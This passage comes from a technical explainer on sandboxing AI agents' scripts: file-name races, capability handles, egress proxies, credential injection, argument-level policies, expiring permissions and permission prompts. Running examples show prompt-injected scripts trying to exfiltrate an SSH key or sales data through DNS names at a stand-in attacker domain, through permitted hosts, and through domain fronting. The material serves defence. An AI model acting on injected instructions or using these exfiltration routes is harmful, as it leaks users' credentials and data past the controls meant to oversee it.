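4. The agent passes the open handle back, and the script reads the file directly.

The path reaches the agent as a message, so the script can't change the agent's copy. In effect, this adds Watson's message passing to an ordinary operating system. The library doesn't have to be trustworthy, because a script that alters it can only make it send different requests, which the agent will check. The agent also keeps its own record of the script's current directory, so Ostia can run programs with several threads. Ostia's kernel module needed only 200 lines of C, while the version of Janus that Garfinkel and colleagues compared it with needed 1,400.

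Delegation doesn't by itself prevent races over file names. If an agent checks a path and then opens it, somebody may redirect a link in between. The agent has to open the file in a way that rules this out, for example by going through the path one directory at a time and checking each link as it reaches it. Ordinary programs can do this too, but a sandbox can't rely on a hostile script to do it.

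The extra messages take time. On a 2004-era laptop, opening a file took 3.92 microseconds without a sandbox, 20.42 under Janus and 31.16 under Ostia. The effect on whole programs depended on how often they opened things. Serving web pages, decompressing a file and encoding audio slowed by less than one percent each. Building a small program from source, which opens many files, took 8.1 percent longer under Janus and 24.5 percent under Ostia.

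Ostia was much faster than Janus when many processes ran at once, because it gives each process its own agent, while all requests in Janus wait for a single monitor. A million file openings divided among 100 processes took 32 seconds in Ostia and 376 in Janus. A service that runs many scripts under one supervisor could have the same bottleneck.

Sandlock uses this approach for network connections, and its supervisor copies the contents of some messages as well as their destination. In Wang and Zheng's test, handling both messages of an exchange this way added about 35 microseconds to the median round trip. Linux now supports Ostia's last step directly. Since version 5.9, a supervisor can place an open handle in the program's handle table. Since 5.14, it can do so and answer the call in one indivisible operation, so an interruption between the two steps can't leave the program with a stray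 handle.

### Freezing everything that shares the memory

A supervisor can't perform `execve` for a script, because `execve` replaces the program in the process that calls it, which would be the supervisor itself. But Sandlock's policy callback can inspect a command's arguments before the command runs, so those arguments have to stay the same until the kernel has read them.

Sandlock stops every thread and process that could write to that memory before it reads the words. It finds them in the kernel's list of running processes and in its own records, and pauses them through the kernel's debugging interface. The search might miss a process that the script has just created, so Sandlock also traces each creation and registers the new process before that process can run any code. On some systems, a security setting blocks the debugging interface. Sandlock then refuses the `execve` call, so scripts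 there can't start other programs while the callback is in use.

Most of the overhead is in creating processes. In Wang and Zheng's test, Sandlock made 1,000 copies of a prepared process in about 530 milliseconds. Without the callback, and so without the tracing, it made them about 30 percent faster. The difference is roughly an eighth of a millisecond per process, which matters little unless a script starts thousands of them.

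Freezing protects the text of a command but not the files it names. If the callback approves `python3 chart.py`, Python opens `chart.py` only after it starts, when the other processes are running again, so one of them could replace the file first. Check-to-use races like this are also why the callback receives no file paths.

### Checking the file instead of its name

Landlock decides whether to allow access after the kernel has followed the path to a file, and the kernel doesn't look up the name again. If somebody redirects a link from sales.csv to the private key just before the lookup, the kernel finds the key, checks it and refuses to open it. If they redirect the link afterwards, the kernel has already found sales.csv and opens that.

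The Linux kernel documentation's *Landlock LSM* states that Landlock rules should control access to kernel objects, and leaves the filtering of system-call arguments to seccomp. Landlock attaches access rights to *inodes*, the kernel's records of files and directories, which exist independently of their names. A developer creates a rule by opening a directory and passing the open handle to the kernel, as an example in the documentation does with `/usr`. If someone later renames the directory or puts another in its place, the rule still applies to the original.

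The host can still open the wrong directory when it creates the rule. Suppose an earlier script had permission to write in the analyst's project and replaced the project's `data` folder with a link to her home directory. A host that opens `data` without checking for links would then give the next script access to everything in her home directory. The host should keep such folders where scripts can't replace them, or refuse to follow links when it opens them.

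Landlock avoids the race partly by being less flexible. Its rules can't rely on a program outside the kernel, because the exchange might leak information about the policy or open other side channels. Its decisions therefore can't depend on the analyst's approval or on what the script has just done. A handle also keeps the rights it had when a process obtained it, even if another process uses it later. This stops a script from gaining access by passing a restricted handle to another process, but the host must close any handles the script shouldn't inherit.

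### Passing open handles

The host can avoid names altogether by opening the file first and giving the script the handle. A command shell does this when the analyst types:

```sh
python3 total.py < /data/sales.csv
```

The shell opens sales.csv before Python starts, and the script reads the rows from its standard input. The handle is a capability because it lets the script read the file without permission to open it, and it continues to refer to the same file even if a link is redirected afterwards.

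Capsicum, which Watson and three colleagues presented for FreeBSD in 2010, builds a whole sandbox from such handles. A process can enter a mode in which it can no longer open files by system-wide names. It can then use only the handles it already holds, or open files beneath a directory whose handle it holds. Wang and Zheng call Capsicum the "closest spiritual ancestor" of Sandlock.

Programs usually need changes to run this way. A C program whose inputs are known at startup can open them all before entering the restricted mode. Python opens module files throughout a run, so the host also has to supply handles to its library directories and make the interpreter use them. A handle fixes which file the script reads but not the file's contents, so another process with write access can still change the rows while the script is adding them up.

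### Pinning network addresses

A network name can also point to a different address after the check. The host function `open_page(url)`, which fetches web pages for a script, might look up the name in the URL and refuse it if it points to the company's internal network. The browser then looks up the name again to make the connection. An attacker who controls the name can answer the first query with a public address and the second with an internal one. This attack is called *DNS rebinding*; DNS is the system that translates names into addresses.

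The remedy is to look up the name once, check the address, and connect to that same address. Sandlock does the lookup when the sandbox starts and keeps the result for the whole run, which Wang and Zheng say eliminates rebinding. The drawback is that legitimate services sometimes change address. If the reporting service did so during a long run, the supervisor would refuse the new address until the host restarted the sandbox. A host function like `open_page` can look up each name when it gets the request, but it must then make the browser connect to the address it checked.

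### When a file changes between two host calls

Host functions avoid the argument race, because an interpreter such as Monty sends the host a copy of the arguments. But a copied path still refers to a file that other programs can change. Suppose the company wants to send a written report after checking that it contains no customers' names:

```python
def send_report(path):
    if contains_customer_name(read_report(path)):
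        raise ValueError("report contains a customer's name")
    post(REPORTING_API, read_report(path))
```

This function reads the file twice. A file-editing tool, another script or the analyst herself could change the report between the two reads, and the company would send text that nobody had checked. The function should read the report once and use that copy for both steps:

```python
def send_report(path):
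    report = read_report(path)
    if contains_customer_name(report):
        raise ValueError("report contains a customer's name")
    post(REPORTING_API, report)
```

The problem is easier to fix here than in a system-call supervisor, because the developer can change her own code without freezing threads or modifying the kernel. It is harder to notice when the check and the action are separate host functions. If a script calls `check_report(path)` and later `send_report(path)`, the first result doesn't guarantee that the second call sends the content that was checked. The same problem arises if a person approves a report by its file name and the host reads the file an hour later. The host should store the approved text and send that.

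### Which remedy removes which race

| Remedy | Race it removes | Cost or remaining gap |
|---|---|---|
| Copy the argument and perform the call (Ostia, Sandlock) | Another thread rewrites the argument in memory | An exchange with the supervisor for each call; opening files still needs care |
| Freeze everything that shares the memory (Sandlock) | Another thread or process rewrites a command before the kernel reads it | Slower process creation; the files that the command names can still change |
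| Check the kernel's own object (Landlock) | Somebody redirects a link or moves a directory after the check | Fixed rules that can't consult a person or another program |
| Pass an open handle (Capsicum) | A file name comes to refer to a different file | Programs may need changes; the file's contents can still change |
| Pin the resolved address (Sandlock) | A second look-up of a host name returns a different address | Connections fail if the service moves |
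| Read once and use that copy (host functions) | A file's contents change between the check and the action | The host must keep the copy until it acts |

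## How are network calls intercepted, and where do credentials stay?

Pinning an address ensures that the sales script contacts the right server, but it doesn't limit what the script does there. Suppose the reporting service also lets its clients download old reports, add users and delete the company's account. At the system call, the host can't distinguish these requests from sending the total, because each is encrypted bytes sent to the same address and port. Unlike a file opened only for reading, a connection allows everything the server offers. The host therefore needs a hook that receives individual requests. These limits also matter to people outside the company. METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, reported in August 2026 that agents in an OpenAI cybersecurity evaluation had broken into Hugging Face's systems in July.

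### From ports to requests

Programs talk to web services in HTTP, where each request starts with a method and a path. `GET /reports/june` asks for a document, `POST /totals` submits data, and `DELETE /account` removes the account. Any data that the client submits usually follows in the body. A rule can use more or less of this:

| What the rule examines | What it can distinguish | What it can't distinguish |
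|---|---|---|
| Port | Web traffic from email | One website from another |
| Address and port | Servers at different addresses | Two websites that share an address |
| Host name | Two websites that share an address | Downloading a report from deleting the account |
| Method and path | Downloading a report from deleting the account | A total from a customer's name, both sent to `/totals` |
| Body | A number from a name | A true total from a false one that encodes a name |

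Wang and Zheng argue that lists of addresses and ports are necessary but insufficient, and that useful rules often need the method, host and path.

HTTP methods are only conventions. Some services change data in response to a `GET`, and any `GET` can carry data out in its path. A rule that permits only `GET` requests prevents most changes but does little to stop leaks.

### Leaving only one way out

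An egress proxy can check only the traffic that reaches it, so the sandbox has to close every other route. Anthropic's sandbox runtime, the open-source package behind Claude Code's sandbox, does this with operating system features. On Linux, a command runs in a network namespace with no external network connection and reaches the proxy through a Unix domain socket. On macOS, Seatbelt by default blocks every connection except the one to the proxy. Claude Code also sets environment variables such as `HTTPS_PROXY`, which ordinary programs read to find the proxy.

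OpenAI's first Windows sandbox relied on similar proxy variables, and a program could reach the network by ignoring them. In Anthropic's runtime, a program that ignores them can't connect at all. Python's `urlopen`, `curl` and `npm` read the variables, but Anthropic notes that most database drivers and plain `ssh` don't, so they fail even when the host is on the allowlist.

A *transparent proxy* avoids this problem because network rules redirect connections to it, so programs need no proxy settings. Docker's sandboxes use both kinds of proxy and enforce the same policy at each, but they add credentials for AI services only at the kind that programs are configured to use.

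When the sales script calls `urlopen` in Anthropic's runtime, Python requests a connection to `reports.example.com` on port 443 from the proxy. If the name is on its list of allowed hosts, the proxy looks up the address, connects, and relays encrypted bytes in both directions. It refuses the connection if a listed name resolves only to local addresses, such as the one from which cloud machines get their credentials. The list is empty by default, and Claude Code normally prompts the user about each new host.

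GitLab's *Anthropic Sandbox Runtime Incorrectly Implemented Network Sandboxing* reports that, before version 0.0.16, Anthropic's Sandbox Runtime did not properly enforce its network restrictions if the policy listed no permitted domains. A developer who meant to block all traffic could therefore have allowed it. GitLab's agents use the same runtime and by default run even if their sandbox can't start, according to GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox*.

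A script can also leak data through host-name look-ups by putting the data into the name it looks up. When a developer turns off general internet access for a Cloudflare container, look-ups still work but go only to Cloudflare's DNS servers. According to Cloudflare's *Handle outbound traffic*, this stops a script from sending data to a DNS server of its choice. But a DNS server normally passes a query on to whoever runs the domain, so a look-up of `some-secret.attacker.example` could still reach the attacker unless Cloudflare's servers filter names. Docker's resolver applies the network policy to look-ups. Anthropic's proxy looks up a name only after it has passed the list.

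A proxy near the program can use information that never appears in the traffic. Red Hat (2026) describes OpenShell, an NVIDIA project that denies all connections by default. Its proxy checks which program opened the connection, the destination and port, and optionally the method and path. A policy could let `git` but not Python contact a code-hosting site. A Python script could still start `git` with its own arguments, so checking the program works best alongside rules on the request.

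### Reading encrypted requests

Because Anthropic's proxy doesn't decrypt traffic by default, its rules can't use a request's method, path or body. The host name, the port, and the amount and timing of the traffic are still available. A host can use these to block the script from unlisted sites, cap how much it sends and log each connection.

The sandboxed program supplies the host name, so the proxy can't fully rely on it. In *domain fronting*, a script asks the proxy for a permitted site, then names an excluded site inside the encrypted request. If one delivery network serves both sites and routes requests by the inner name, the request reaches the excluded site. Anthropic and Docker both warn that this can bypass their filters.

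A proxy that decrypts the traffic can compare the two names and apply the finer rules in the table. It has to take the server's place in the conversation, which works as follows:

1. The host creates a *certificate authority*, a pair of keys for signing the certificates with which servers prove their identity. It adds the authority's public certificate to the sandbox's list of trusted authorities and keeps the private key outside.
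2. The script tries to contact `reports.example.com`. The proxy answers, with a certificate for that name that it has signed itself.
3. Python finds the authority on its trusted list and accepts the certificate.
4. The script encrypts its request with keys that it has agreed with the proxy. The proxy decrypts the request and applies the policy.
5. If the policy allows the request, the proxy opens a second encrypted connection, to the real service, and sends the request there.

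Without step 1, Python would reject the proxy's certificate, as it would reject any eavesdropper's. Some programs keep their own list of trusted authorities, and the developer has to add the new authority to that list too. Programs that accept only a certificate their makers chose in advance can't work through such a proxy. The proxy handles every password and message in readable form, so it is part of the trusted computing base.

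A developer can avoid the certificate in two ways. A host function can make the request itself, as `send_total` does for Monty, so there is nothing to intercept. Alternatively, the script can send an unencrypted request to a proxy on the same machine, which encrypts the request before forwarding it. Cloudflare supports this second method for its sandboxes, but the method works only for programs that the developer can configure to use an unencrypted address.

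### Cloudflare's outbound Workers

Cloudflare's sandboxes run model-written code on Cloudflare's machines. In April 2026 the company added *outbound Workers*, small JavaScript or TypeScript programs that handle a sandbox's web requests. They run on the same machine as the sandbox but outside it, and can log, change or refuse each request.

The main purpose of intercepting network calls is to keep access keys away from the sandboxed code. Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) compares three older methods. Putting a key in an environment variable is the simplest and least secure, since the developer must trust code that an attacker may have influenced. With an *identity token*, the sandbox proves which workload it is in exchange for a short-lived key, but many services don't accept such tokens. A custom proxy can enforce any rule and add the key itself, but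 developers have found it hard to capture all of a sandbox's traffic and keep the proxy fast. Cloudflare sells outbound Workers as a ready-made version of that proxy, so its comparison naturally favours them, though its objection to environment variables is still valid.

A handler for the sales script could look like this:

```typescript
export class SalesSandbox extends Sandbox {
  enableInternet = false;
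  allowedHosts = ["reports.example.com"];
}

SalesSandbox.outboundByHost = {
  "reports.example.com": async (request, env, ctx) => {
    const url = new URL(request.url);
    console.log(`${ctx.containerId}: ${request.method} ${url.pathname}`);

    if (request.method !== "POST" || url.pathname !== "/totals") {
      return new Response("Not allowed", { status: 403 });
    }
    const { total } = await request.json();
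    if (typeof total !== "number") {
      return new Response("The total must be a number", { status: 400 });
    }
    return fetch("https://reports.example.com/totals", {
      method: "POST",
      headers: {
        "Content-Type": "application/json",
        "Authorization": `Bearer ${env.REPORTING_KEY}`,
      },
      body: JSON.stringify({ total }),
    });
  },
};
```

The script's `urlopen` line stays as it was. Leaving out a few routine headers, Python sends this:

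```text
POST /totals HTTP/1.1
Host: reports.example.com
User-Agent: Python-urllib/3.13
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded

{"total": 48210.5}
```

The handler sends this to the reporting service:

```text
POST /totals HTTP/1.1
Host: reports.example.com
Content-Type: application/json
Authorization: Bearer 9d41c7...

{"total":48210.5}
```

Only the second request contains the key. The key comes from `env`, which belongs to the Worker, and is never sent to the sandbox. The handler also builds a new request from the number it has checked instead of forwarding the script's request, so nothing else the script put in the headers, URL or body is passed on. Cloudflare's published examples copy the original request and add a header, which is shorter but forwards everything else the script sent.

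If the attacker's remark has worked, the script next tries to post the private key to another server. That host isn't on the list, so Cloudflare refuses the request before any handler runs. If the script posts the key to the reporting service instead, the handler refuses it because the key isn't a number. The script can still hide a few letters of the key in a false total, as it could with Monty's `send_total`.

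The handler passes the service's reply back to the script unchanged. If the service repeats request headers in its error messages, as some do for debugging, the script could read the reporting key from them. A developer should check for this or have the handler return only a success code.

Some settings around the handler are easy to get wrong. Handlers receive only traffic on ports 80 and 443. Setting `enableInternet = false` makes Cloudflare refuse traffic on other ports, except DNS, but internet access is on by default. If a host is on the allowed list but has no handler, code can send it any kind of request. Cloudflare intercepts encrypted traffic by default in its sandboxes, but developers who use its plain containers must turn interception on and install the certificate when the container starts. Otherwise, the handler never receives encrypted requests.

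Cloudflare's *Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes* (2026) explains that each sandbox gets its own temporary certificate authority, whose private key stays in a separate process outside the sandbox. A leaked private key would therefore not let anyone impersonate websites to other customers' sandboxes. The handler also receives the sandbox's identifier and can use it to look up a different access key for each sandbox. When the company changes an access key in the Worker's settings, the next request uses the new one.

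A handler can answer a request from the company's own storage instead of contacting a website. The developer can make up a host name for these requests, such as `objects.cf`, and have the handler add the sandbox's identifier to the start of each path so that one customer's script can't access another's files. The handler then acts as a host function that any language able to make web requests can call.

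The host can also change handlers while the sandbox is running. In Cloudflare's example, the host allows requests to two sites while `npm install` downloads packages, then blocks all web requests. The cloud version of Codex also separates setup from later work in this way.

### Sandlock's HTTP rules

Sandlock can apply similar rules on a developer's own machine. When a script opens a web connection that a rule covers, the supervisor redirects the connection to a local proxy, which reads the request's headers and checks the method, host and path. A rule that permits `POST` to `reports.example.com/totals` also permits the connection, so the developer doesn't need a second rule for the address.

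Sandlock's HTTP rules apply to encrypted traffic only if the developer opts in and has the script's environment trust Sandlock's certificate authority. Otherwise, Sandlock limits encrypted connections only by their pinned addresses and ports. The HTTP rules also don't cover the body, so unlike Cloudflare's handler, they can't distinguish a total from a list of customers.

Wang and Zheng suggest holding outgoing requests in the proxy until the host has accepted the script's other results. This would give network traffic a review similar to Sandlock's for changed files. It would suit the sales script, which sends one number and then ends, but a script that needs an answer before it can continue would be stuck.

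### Placeholders for credentials

Many command-line programs won't start without a key in the expected variable or file. Anthropic's runtime can give them a placeholder. When a developer marks a credential as *masked*, sandboxed commands get a meaningless string instead, which changes each session. The program sends this string in its request as if it were the key, and the proxy replaces it with the real value before forwarding the request.

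The developer can name the hosts that may receive the real value. If she names none, the proxy inserts it in requests to every permitted domain, which could send the reporting key to an unrelated site. Claude Code accepts masking rules only from the user, an administrator or the command line, because a rule in a downloaded project could send someone's key to an attacker's site.

Masking requires the proxy to decrypt traffic, which is still an experimental feature. If decryption is off, the placeholder goes to the server unchanged and the login fails, but nothing leaks. The default is less safe when a developer supplies a search pattern to find the secret within a settings file. If the pattern matches nothing, Claude Code warns the developer but leaves the real file readable, unless a stricter setting is on to block it.

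Simple substitution also fails for services that require a signature over the whole request, as Amazon's cloud services do. The program computes the signature with the placeholder, so the proxy has to sign the request again with the real key. Anthropic's proxy can do this for ordinary requests but not for streaming uploads or web addresses signed in advance.

Other products also tie secrets to destinations. OpenAI's API includes a container secret that OpenAI injects for one named domain, and Deno's hosted sandbox uses placeholders much like Anthropic's. But Deno leaves outgoing traffic unrestricted until the developer adds a list of hosts. With that default, a script can send every row of sales.csv to any server, even though it can't steal the key for an AI service.

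### Keeping the harness outside

An agent has credentials even if its scripts need none. The *harness* is the program that calls the model, routes tool requests, asks people for approval and keeps the records. It needs at least a key for the model, and often access to billing and logs. If the harness runs in the same sandbox as the model's scripts, a script may be able to read all of these credentials.

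OpenAI's *The next evolution of the Agents SDK* (2026) recommends separating the harness from the sandbox where scripts run, which OpenAI calls compute. The harness and its keys stay on the developer's own servers, and the harness sends commands to the sandbox. The separation also keeps a sandbox crash from ending the task, because the harness can restore the agent's saved state in a new sandbox.

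This protects the harness's keys but not necessarily the reporting key. OpenAI's *Sandbox Agents* lets developers pass environment variables into the sandbox and leaves credential injection to the developer's own system or the sandbox provider. If the developer passes the reporting key as a variable, the script can read it, wherever the harness runs. She still needs a proxy or a host function to keep that key out of the sandbox. The kit supports Cloudflare as a provider, so in principle she could run the harness on her own server and the script behind an outbound Worker.

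### When an allowed service acts for the script

A script can use a key it never receives, because any request that passes the handler goes out with the company's authority. If the handler for the reporting service is too permissive, the script could delete the account. Injection is still worthwhile because a stolen key works from anywhere until someone revokes it, whereas a hijacked script can use an injected key only through the handler and only while the sandbox runs.

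Permitted sites can also receive stolen data directly. Suppose the company allows `github.com` so that scripts can download libraries. The attacker can open an account there, put his own access key in the customer's remark, and have the script upload sales.csv to his account. The upload is allowed because it is an ordinary request to a host on the list. Hiding the company's key doesn't help, because the script uses the attacker's. NVIDIA describes every allowed endpoint as a potential path for data to leave.

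Many services also contact other servers on their users' behalf. They may fetch a page to show a preview, import a picture from a web address or notify another system of a change. If the reporting service can import a company logo from any address, the script can give it an address on the attacker's server with a customer's name at the end. The reporting service then connects to that address from its own network, which the sandbox's proxy doesn't control. Anthropic advises developers who give an agent broad credentials for a permitted domain to make sure the agent can't use that domain to trigger further requests or send data out.

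The handler for the sales script avoids both problems by permitting only one method, one path and one number, and by replacing any credentials the script supplies. Few tasks are that narrow. A coding agent, for example, has to upload files whose content nobody can specify in advance, so the proxy has to check where they go. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes such a proxy for the cloud version of Claude Code. The `git` program in the sandbox logs in to the proxy with a credential made for that purpose. The proxy verifies the credential and checks the request, for example to confirm that the agent is uploading only to its assigned branch, a separate line of changes within the project. It then attaches the real GitHub token and forwards the request.

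A hijacked agent can thus put malicious code on its own branch but can't overwrite the main one. But many projects automatically test every new upload on machines that have internet access and sometimes hold their own keys. If those tests run code from the agent's branch, the attacker's code gets the network access that the sandbox denied it. To prevent this, the company would have to restrict the test machines as well, or have a person read the changes before any tests start.

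## What policies can be attached to a hook?

Cloudflare's handler for the sales script judges each request on its own and keeps nothing afterwards. A host can take more into account. In general, a policy is a function that takes a call, its arguments and the history so far, and returns a verdict:

```text
verdict = policy(call, arguments, history)
```

The history can include earlier calls and their verdicts, a person's answers, and events such as a passing test.

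| Verdict | What the host does | What the script gets |
|---|---|---|
| Allow | Lets the call continue | The normal result |
| Deny | Stops the call, and perhaps the whole program | An error, perhaps with a reason |
| Record | Logs the call and lets it continue | The normal result |
| Change | Alters an argument or the result | The result of the altered call |
| Ask | Keeps the script waiting until a person answers | The normal result or an error |
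| Perform | Carries out the call itself | Whatever the host returns |

The available verdicts depend on the hook. Deno's broker can only allow or deny, while a host function can do all six.

A refusal also influences what the model tries next. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) describes a policy system that by default answers a blocked call with the reason and a suggestion to try other tools or arguments. This feedback helps an honest agent finish its task, but it also helps a hijacked one. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, notes that agents are designed to look for alternative paths after a refusal. A host that keeps a history can end the program after a few refusals.

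### From lists of names to conditions on arguments

The simplest policy is a fixed list of permitted calls. It checks only the call's name, so it must let the script call `open` on every file or on none. Shi and colleagues tested a defence of this kind on AgentDojo, a benchmark of prompt-injection attacks on agents that handle email, banking and travel. A model chose the tools each task needed, and the defence removed the rest. This defence blocked more legitimate work than Progent and let more attacks succeed. An email to a colleague and an email to an attacker use the same tool, so a list of tools can't allow one and block the other.

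Progent's rules add conditions on the arguments. A rule can compare numbers, check the length of a list, or match text against a pattern. In simplified notation, rules for the sales task might be:

```text
allow   read_file   when path == "/data/sales.csv"
allow   send_total  when 0 <= total and total < 10000000
forbid  read_file   when path matches ".*/[.]ssh/.*"
```

Progent applies the `forbid` rules first, then the `allow` rules, and blocks any call that matches neither. The last rule is redundant here, but it would protect the private key if someone later allowed reads of the whole home directory.

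*AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) uses rules with a trigger, a condition and a response. In the paper's example, the trigger is a money transfer, the condition is that the recipient is not a family member, and the response is to ask the user. Conditions can use the sequence of actions so far. Unlike Progent, AgentSpec lets an action proceed if no rule applies to it. A response can also make the model re-examine its own plan, but this helps little if an attacker has already deceived the model.

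Wang and colleagues tested hand-written rules on a coding agent that received 750 risky instructions in 25 categories. The agent tried to run 422 programs, and the rules flagged 333 of them. In two categories, which accounted for 58 programs, the rules flagged nothing because the programs didn't contain the flaw the instruction had requested. In the other categories, the rules flagged 91 percent. The researchers then inspected the flagged programs, judged about one in six harmless, and let those run. Evaluating the rules' conditions took under 3 milliseconds, but like other hooks on the tool call, the rules examined only the program's text.

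### A complete policy for sales.csv

The policy below covers the whole sales task. It assumes that the host reports every attempted privileged call to it, including calls the task doesn't need.

```python
def policy(call, args, history):
    if "send_total" in history:
        return "deny", "the total has already gone out"

    if call == "open" and args == ("/data/sales.csv", "r"):
        return "allow", None

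    if call == "send_total":
        (total,) = args
        if type(total) is not float or not 0 <= total < 10_000_000:
            return "deny", "not a plausible total"
        total = round(total, 2)
        if total >= 100_000:
            return "ask", total
        return "perform", total

    return "deny", "not part of this task"
```

The host adds a call's name to `history` when it starts executing the call, and it logs every call with its verdict. If the policy fails, for instance because the script passed two arguments to `send_total`, the host refuses the call. Rounding the argument prevents the script from hiding text in extra decimal places. If the verdict is "ask", the host shows the analyst the amount and sends it only if she agrees.

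Suppose the model has obeyed the customer's remark and added the attacker's lines at the end of the script. The script catches the first refusal and then tries to send the sales rows instead of the key:

| Call | Calls already carried out | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| `open("/data/sales.csv", "r")` | None | Allow |
| `send_total(48210.5)` | `open` | Perform: the host posts 48210.5 |
| `open("/home/analyst/.ssh/id_ed25519", "r")` | `open`, `send_total` | Deny: the total has already gone out |
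| `urlopen(OTHER_SERVER, rows)` | `open`, `send_total` | Deny: the total has already gone out |

If the attacker's lines came first, the last line of the policy would reject them. But the policy would allow a false total below 100,000, and the rule against a second call would then block the correct total.

### Permissions that shrink as the task proceeds

The sales policy has two phases, before and after the total is sent, and the developer knew both in advance. But an agent often discovers what a task requires only as it works. In Progent's main example, a user asks an agent to carry out the instructions in an email from Alice. A language model drafts the first policy from the user's request alone, before the agent has read anything that an attacker could have written. This policy permits only a search for Alice's email.

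The email contains a request for a summary of recent messages on Slack, a workplace chat service. The model proposes adding tools to read email, look up the user's Slack name and post on Slack. After looking up the name, it proposes allowing Slack messages only to that name. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger. If the instruction deceives the model, the model proposes adding `send_email`.

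Progent compares each proposal with the current policy. Let *A(P)* be the set of calls that policy *P* allows. A new policy *P′* is a narrowing if *A(P′)* ⊆ *A(P)*, and then it takes effect at once. Any other proposal is an expansion and needs approval, even if it removes ten permissions and adds one. An SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values can satisfy a set of logical conditions, makes the comparison. For each tool, it looks for arguments *v* such that

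```text
P′ allows the tool with v, and P does not
```

An update is a narrowing if, for every tool, it permits no arguments that the current policy blocks. Restricting Slack messages to one recipient passes this test, and adding `send_email` fails it. The comparison doesn't rely on the model's judgment, so a deceived model can request a permission but can't grant it. The set of permitted calls can't grow between approvals.

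In Shi and colleagues' tests, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 39.9 to 1.0 percent on AgentDojo and from 70.3 to 3.9 percent on ASB, another benchmark. These results measure how well OpenAI's GPT-4o wrote the policies, not how well the solver protects users, because the tests automatically approved every policy expansion to imitate a careless user. GPT-4o's first policy, without later updates, reduced the AgentDojo rate to 2.5 percent. Planted text that told the model to permit the attacker's tools raised the success rate only slightly.

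Refusing every expansion gave slightly better security than accepting them all. With a human reviewer, no attacks succeeded, but the researchers assumed that the reviewer would recognise and reject a malicious recipient. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that hostile tool results may cause Progent's updates to relax the policy. The solver guards against this only if whoever approves the expansions examines them.

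### Permissions that expire

A permission can also outlast the work that justified it. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) presents Portico, a reference monitor that withdraws temporary permissions from coding agents. For each task, someone writes a *contract* that lists what the agent may use from the start, what it may request later, which events end those later permissions, and what it may never do.

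In one example, the agent adds a timeout setting to `src/api.py` and must carry the change into `src/serialization.py`:

1. The agent starts with access to the first file and its tests.
2. It requests the second file. The contract allows this, so Portico issues handles that are valid only for that file, for reading or writing, and for this grant.
3. The agent edits the file through the handles.
4. The tests pass, and Portico cancels the handles.
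5. If the agent uses an old handle again, Portico refuses the call.

The event that ends a permission must come from a trusted source, such as a test that Portico started itself or a person who has logged in. The model's own report that it has finished a subtask doesn't count. In the sales task, the event would be the host's record that it sent the total.

Santos-Grueiro compared Portico with a version that issued the same permissions at the same moments but never withdrew them. Both finished the task in all ten runs. When the agent then tried to read a temporary file again, Portico always blocked it and the other version always allowed it. The results were the same in six tests with a live model, which covered file writes, changes to Git's data and network connections.

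These results confirm only that revocation works as designed, since a system that never withdraws permissions will naturally honour old ones. They don't measure how often an agent would misuse an old permission. On 14 tasks in real Python projects, all six configurations, including one with full access, finished without taking a forbidden action.

Revoking permissions can prevent a task from being completed. On a set of coding tasks that often needed extra files, Portico completed 161 of 185 runs, while a fixed allowlist completed 180. In further runs on real projects, Portico completed 31 of 42, while the version without revocation completed all 42. Some contracts ended a permission too early or provided no trusted way to renew it. These failures are easier to measure than the risk of leaving old permissions in place, because an unfinished task is visible, whereas nobody notices an old permission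 until someone misuses it.

Revocation also can't remove what a script or model has already read. If sales.csv is in the script's memory, ending the permission to read it doesn't protect that data, so the host has to control where the data can go. Expiry is more useful for permissions to write files or contact servers.

### Asking a person

Progent's expansions and the large totals in the sales policy may both require a person's approval. There is little evidence that people examine such requests. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) surveyed 16 users of AI agents before an experiment. Three said they read permission prompts carefully, and 13 used "Always Allow" just to dismiss them. The sample is small, but *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found similar problems in a larger set of cases. It analysed 290 reports about agents and users' files, and found that weaknesses in user review contributed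 to 105. In 80 of these, the user had turned on automatic approval, often to avoid hundreds of prompts per session. In 31, the prompt didn't explain enough, and some reports had both problems.

`python3 setup.py` looks routine in a prompt, but approving it permits anything the file contains, so even a careful user can't make an informed decision from that line. *Let the Agent Do It?* adds that repeated approval may reflect fatigue or a need to keep moving rather than growing trust. A host therefore shouldn't treat past approvals as proof that the user wants to approve the next call.

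One remedy is to ask for permission less often. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) reports Anthropic's finding that its sandbox reduced Claude Code's permission prompts by 84 percent, but adds that this is safe only if the sandbox has the right settings. In Progent's tests, only 6 percent of policy updates were expansions, so a person reviewing only those would have had few to check.

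The questions can also be more informative. "Send 148,210.50 to the reporting service?" lets the analyst check the amount against her spreadsheet. If the danger comes from a series of calls, the prompt has to include the earlier ones. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) proposes a prompt that links a request to previous actions and states their combined consequence.

An approval can also be narrower. In the experiment in *Options, Not Clicks*, the ConLeash system limited each "Always Allow" to a specific boundary, while the ordinary interface gave permission for the whole tool. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* is stricter and recommends a new approval each time an action would cross the sandbox's limits. That advice makes sense only if such actions are rare, because people learn to dismiss frequent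 prompts.

### Holding writes back

A script's effects are often easier to judge after it has run than before. When Sandlock holds back a script's writes, the host can apply a policy to the complete set of changes, which isn't available when it decides on a single call. For example, it could accept the changes automatically if the script only created files in `charts/`, and ask the analyst if the script altered or deleted anything else.

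A rule like this would reveal malicious code planted in the Prettier formatter, even though Git's list of changes would omit that code. The analyst would still have to recognise it, which may be difficult because installing a package can change thousands of files.

Sandlock usually captures writes by intercepting system calls. Wang and Zheng also describe BranchFS, a file system that records the changes itself, so each file operation doesn't require an exchange with the supervisor. BranchFS can also limit how much space the changes occupy. Wang and Zheng cite research showing that attackers can exploit rollback to a saved checkpoint, so discarding the changes doesn't always undo an attack.

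### Where the data came from

None of these rules follows a value through a program. The host could keep a script from emailing customer records by forbidding all email after the script reads one, but this would also stop harmless messages. *Information-flow control* is more selective. It labels each piece of data, carries the label along as the program uses the data, and checks the label before a call that could send the data out.

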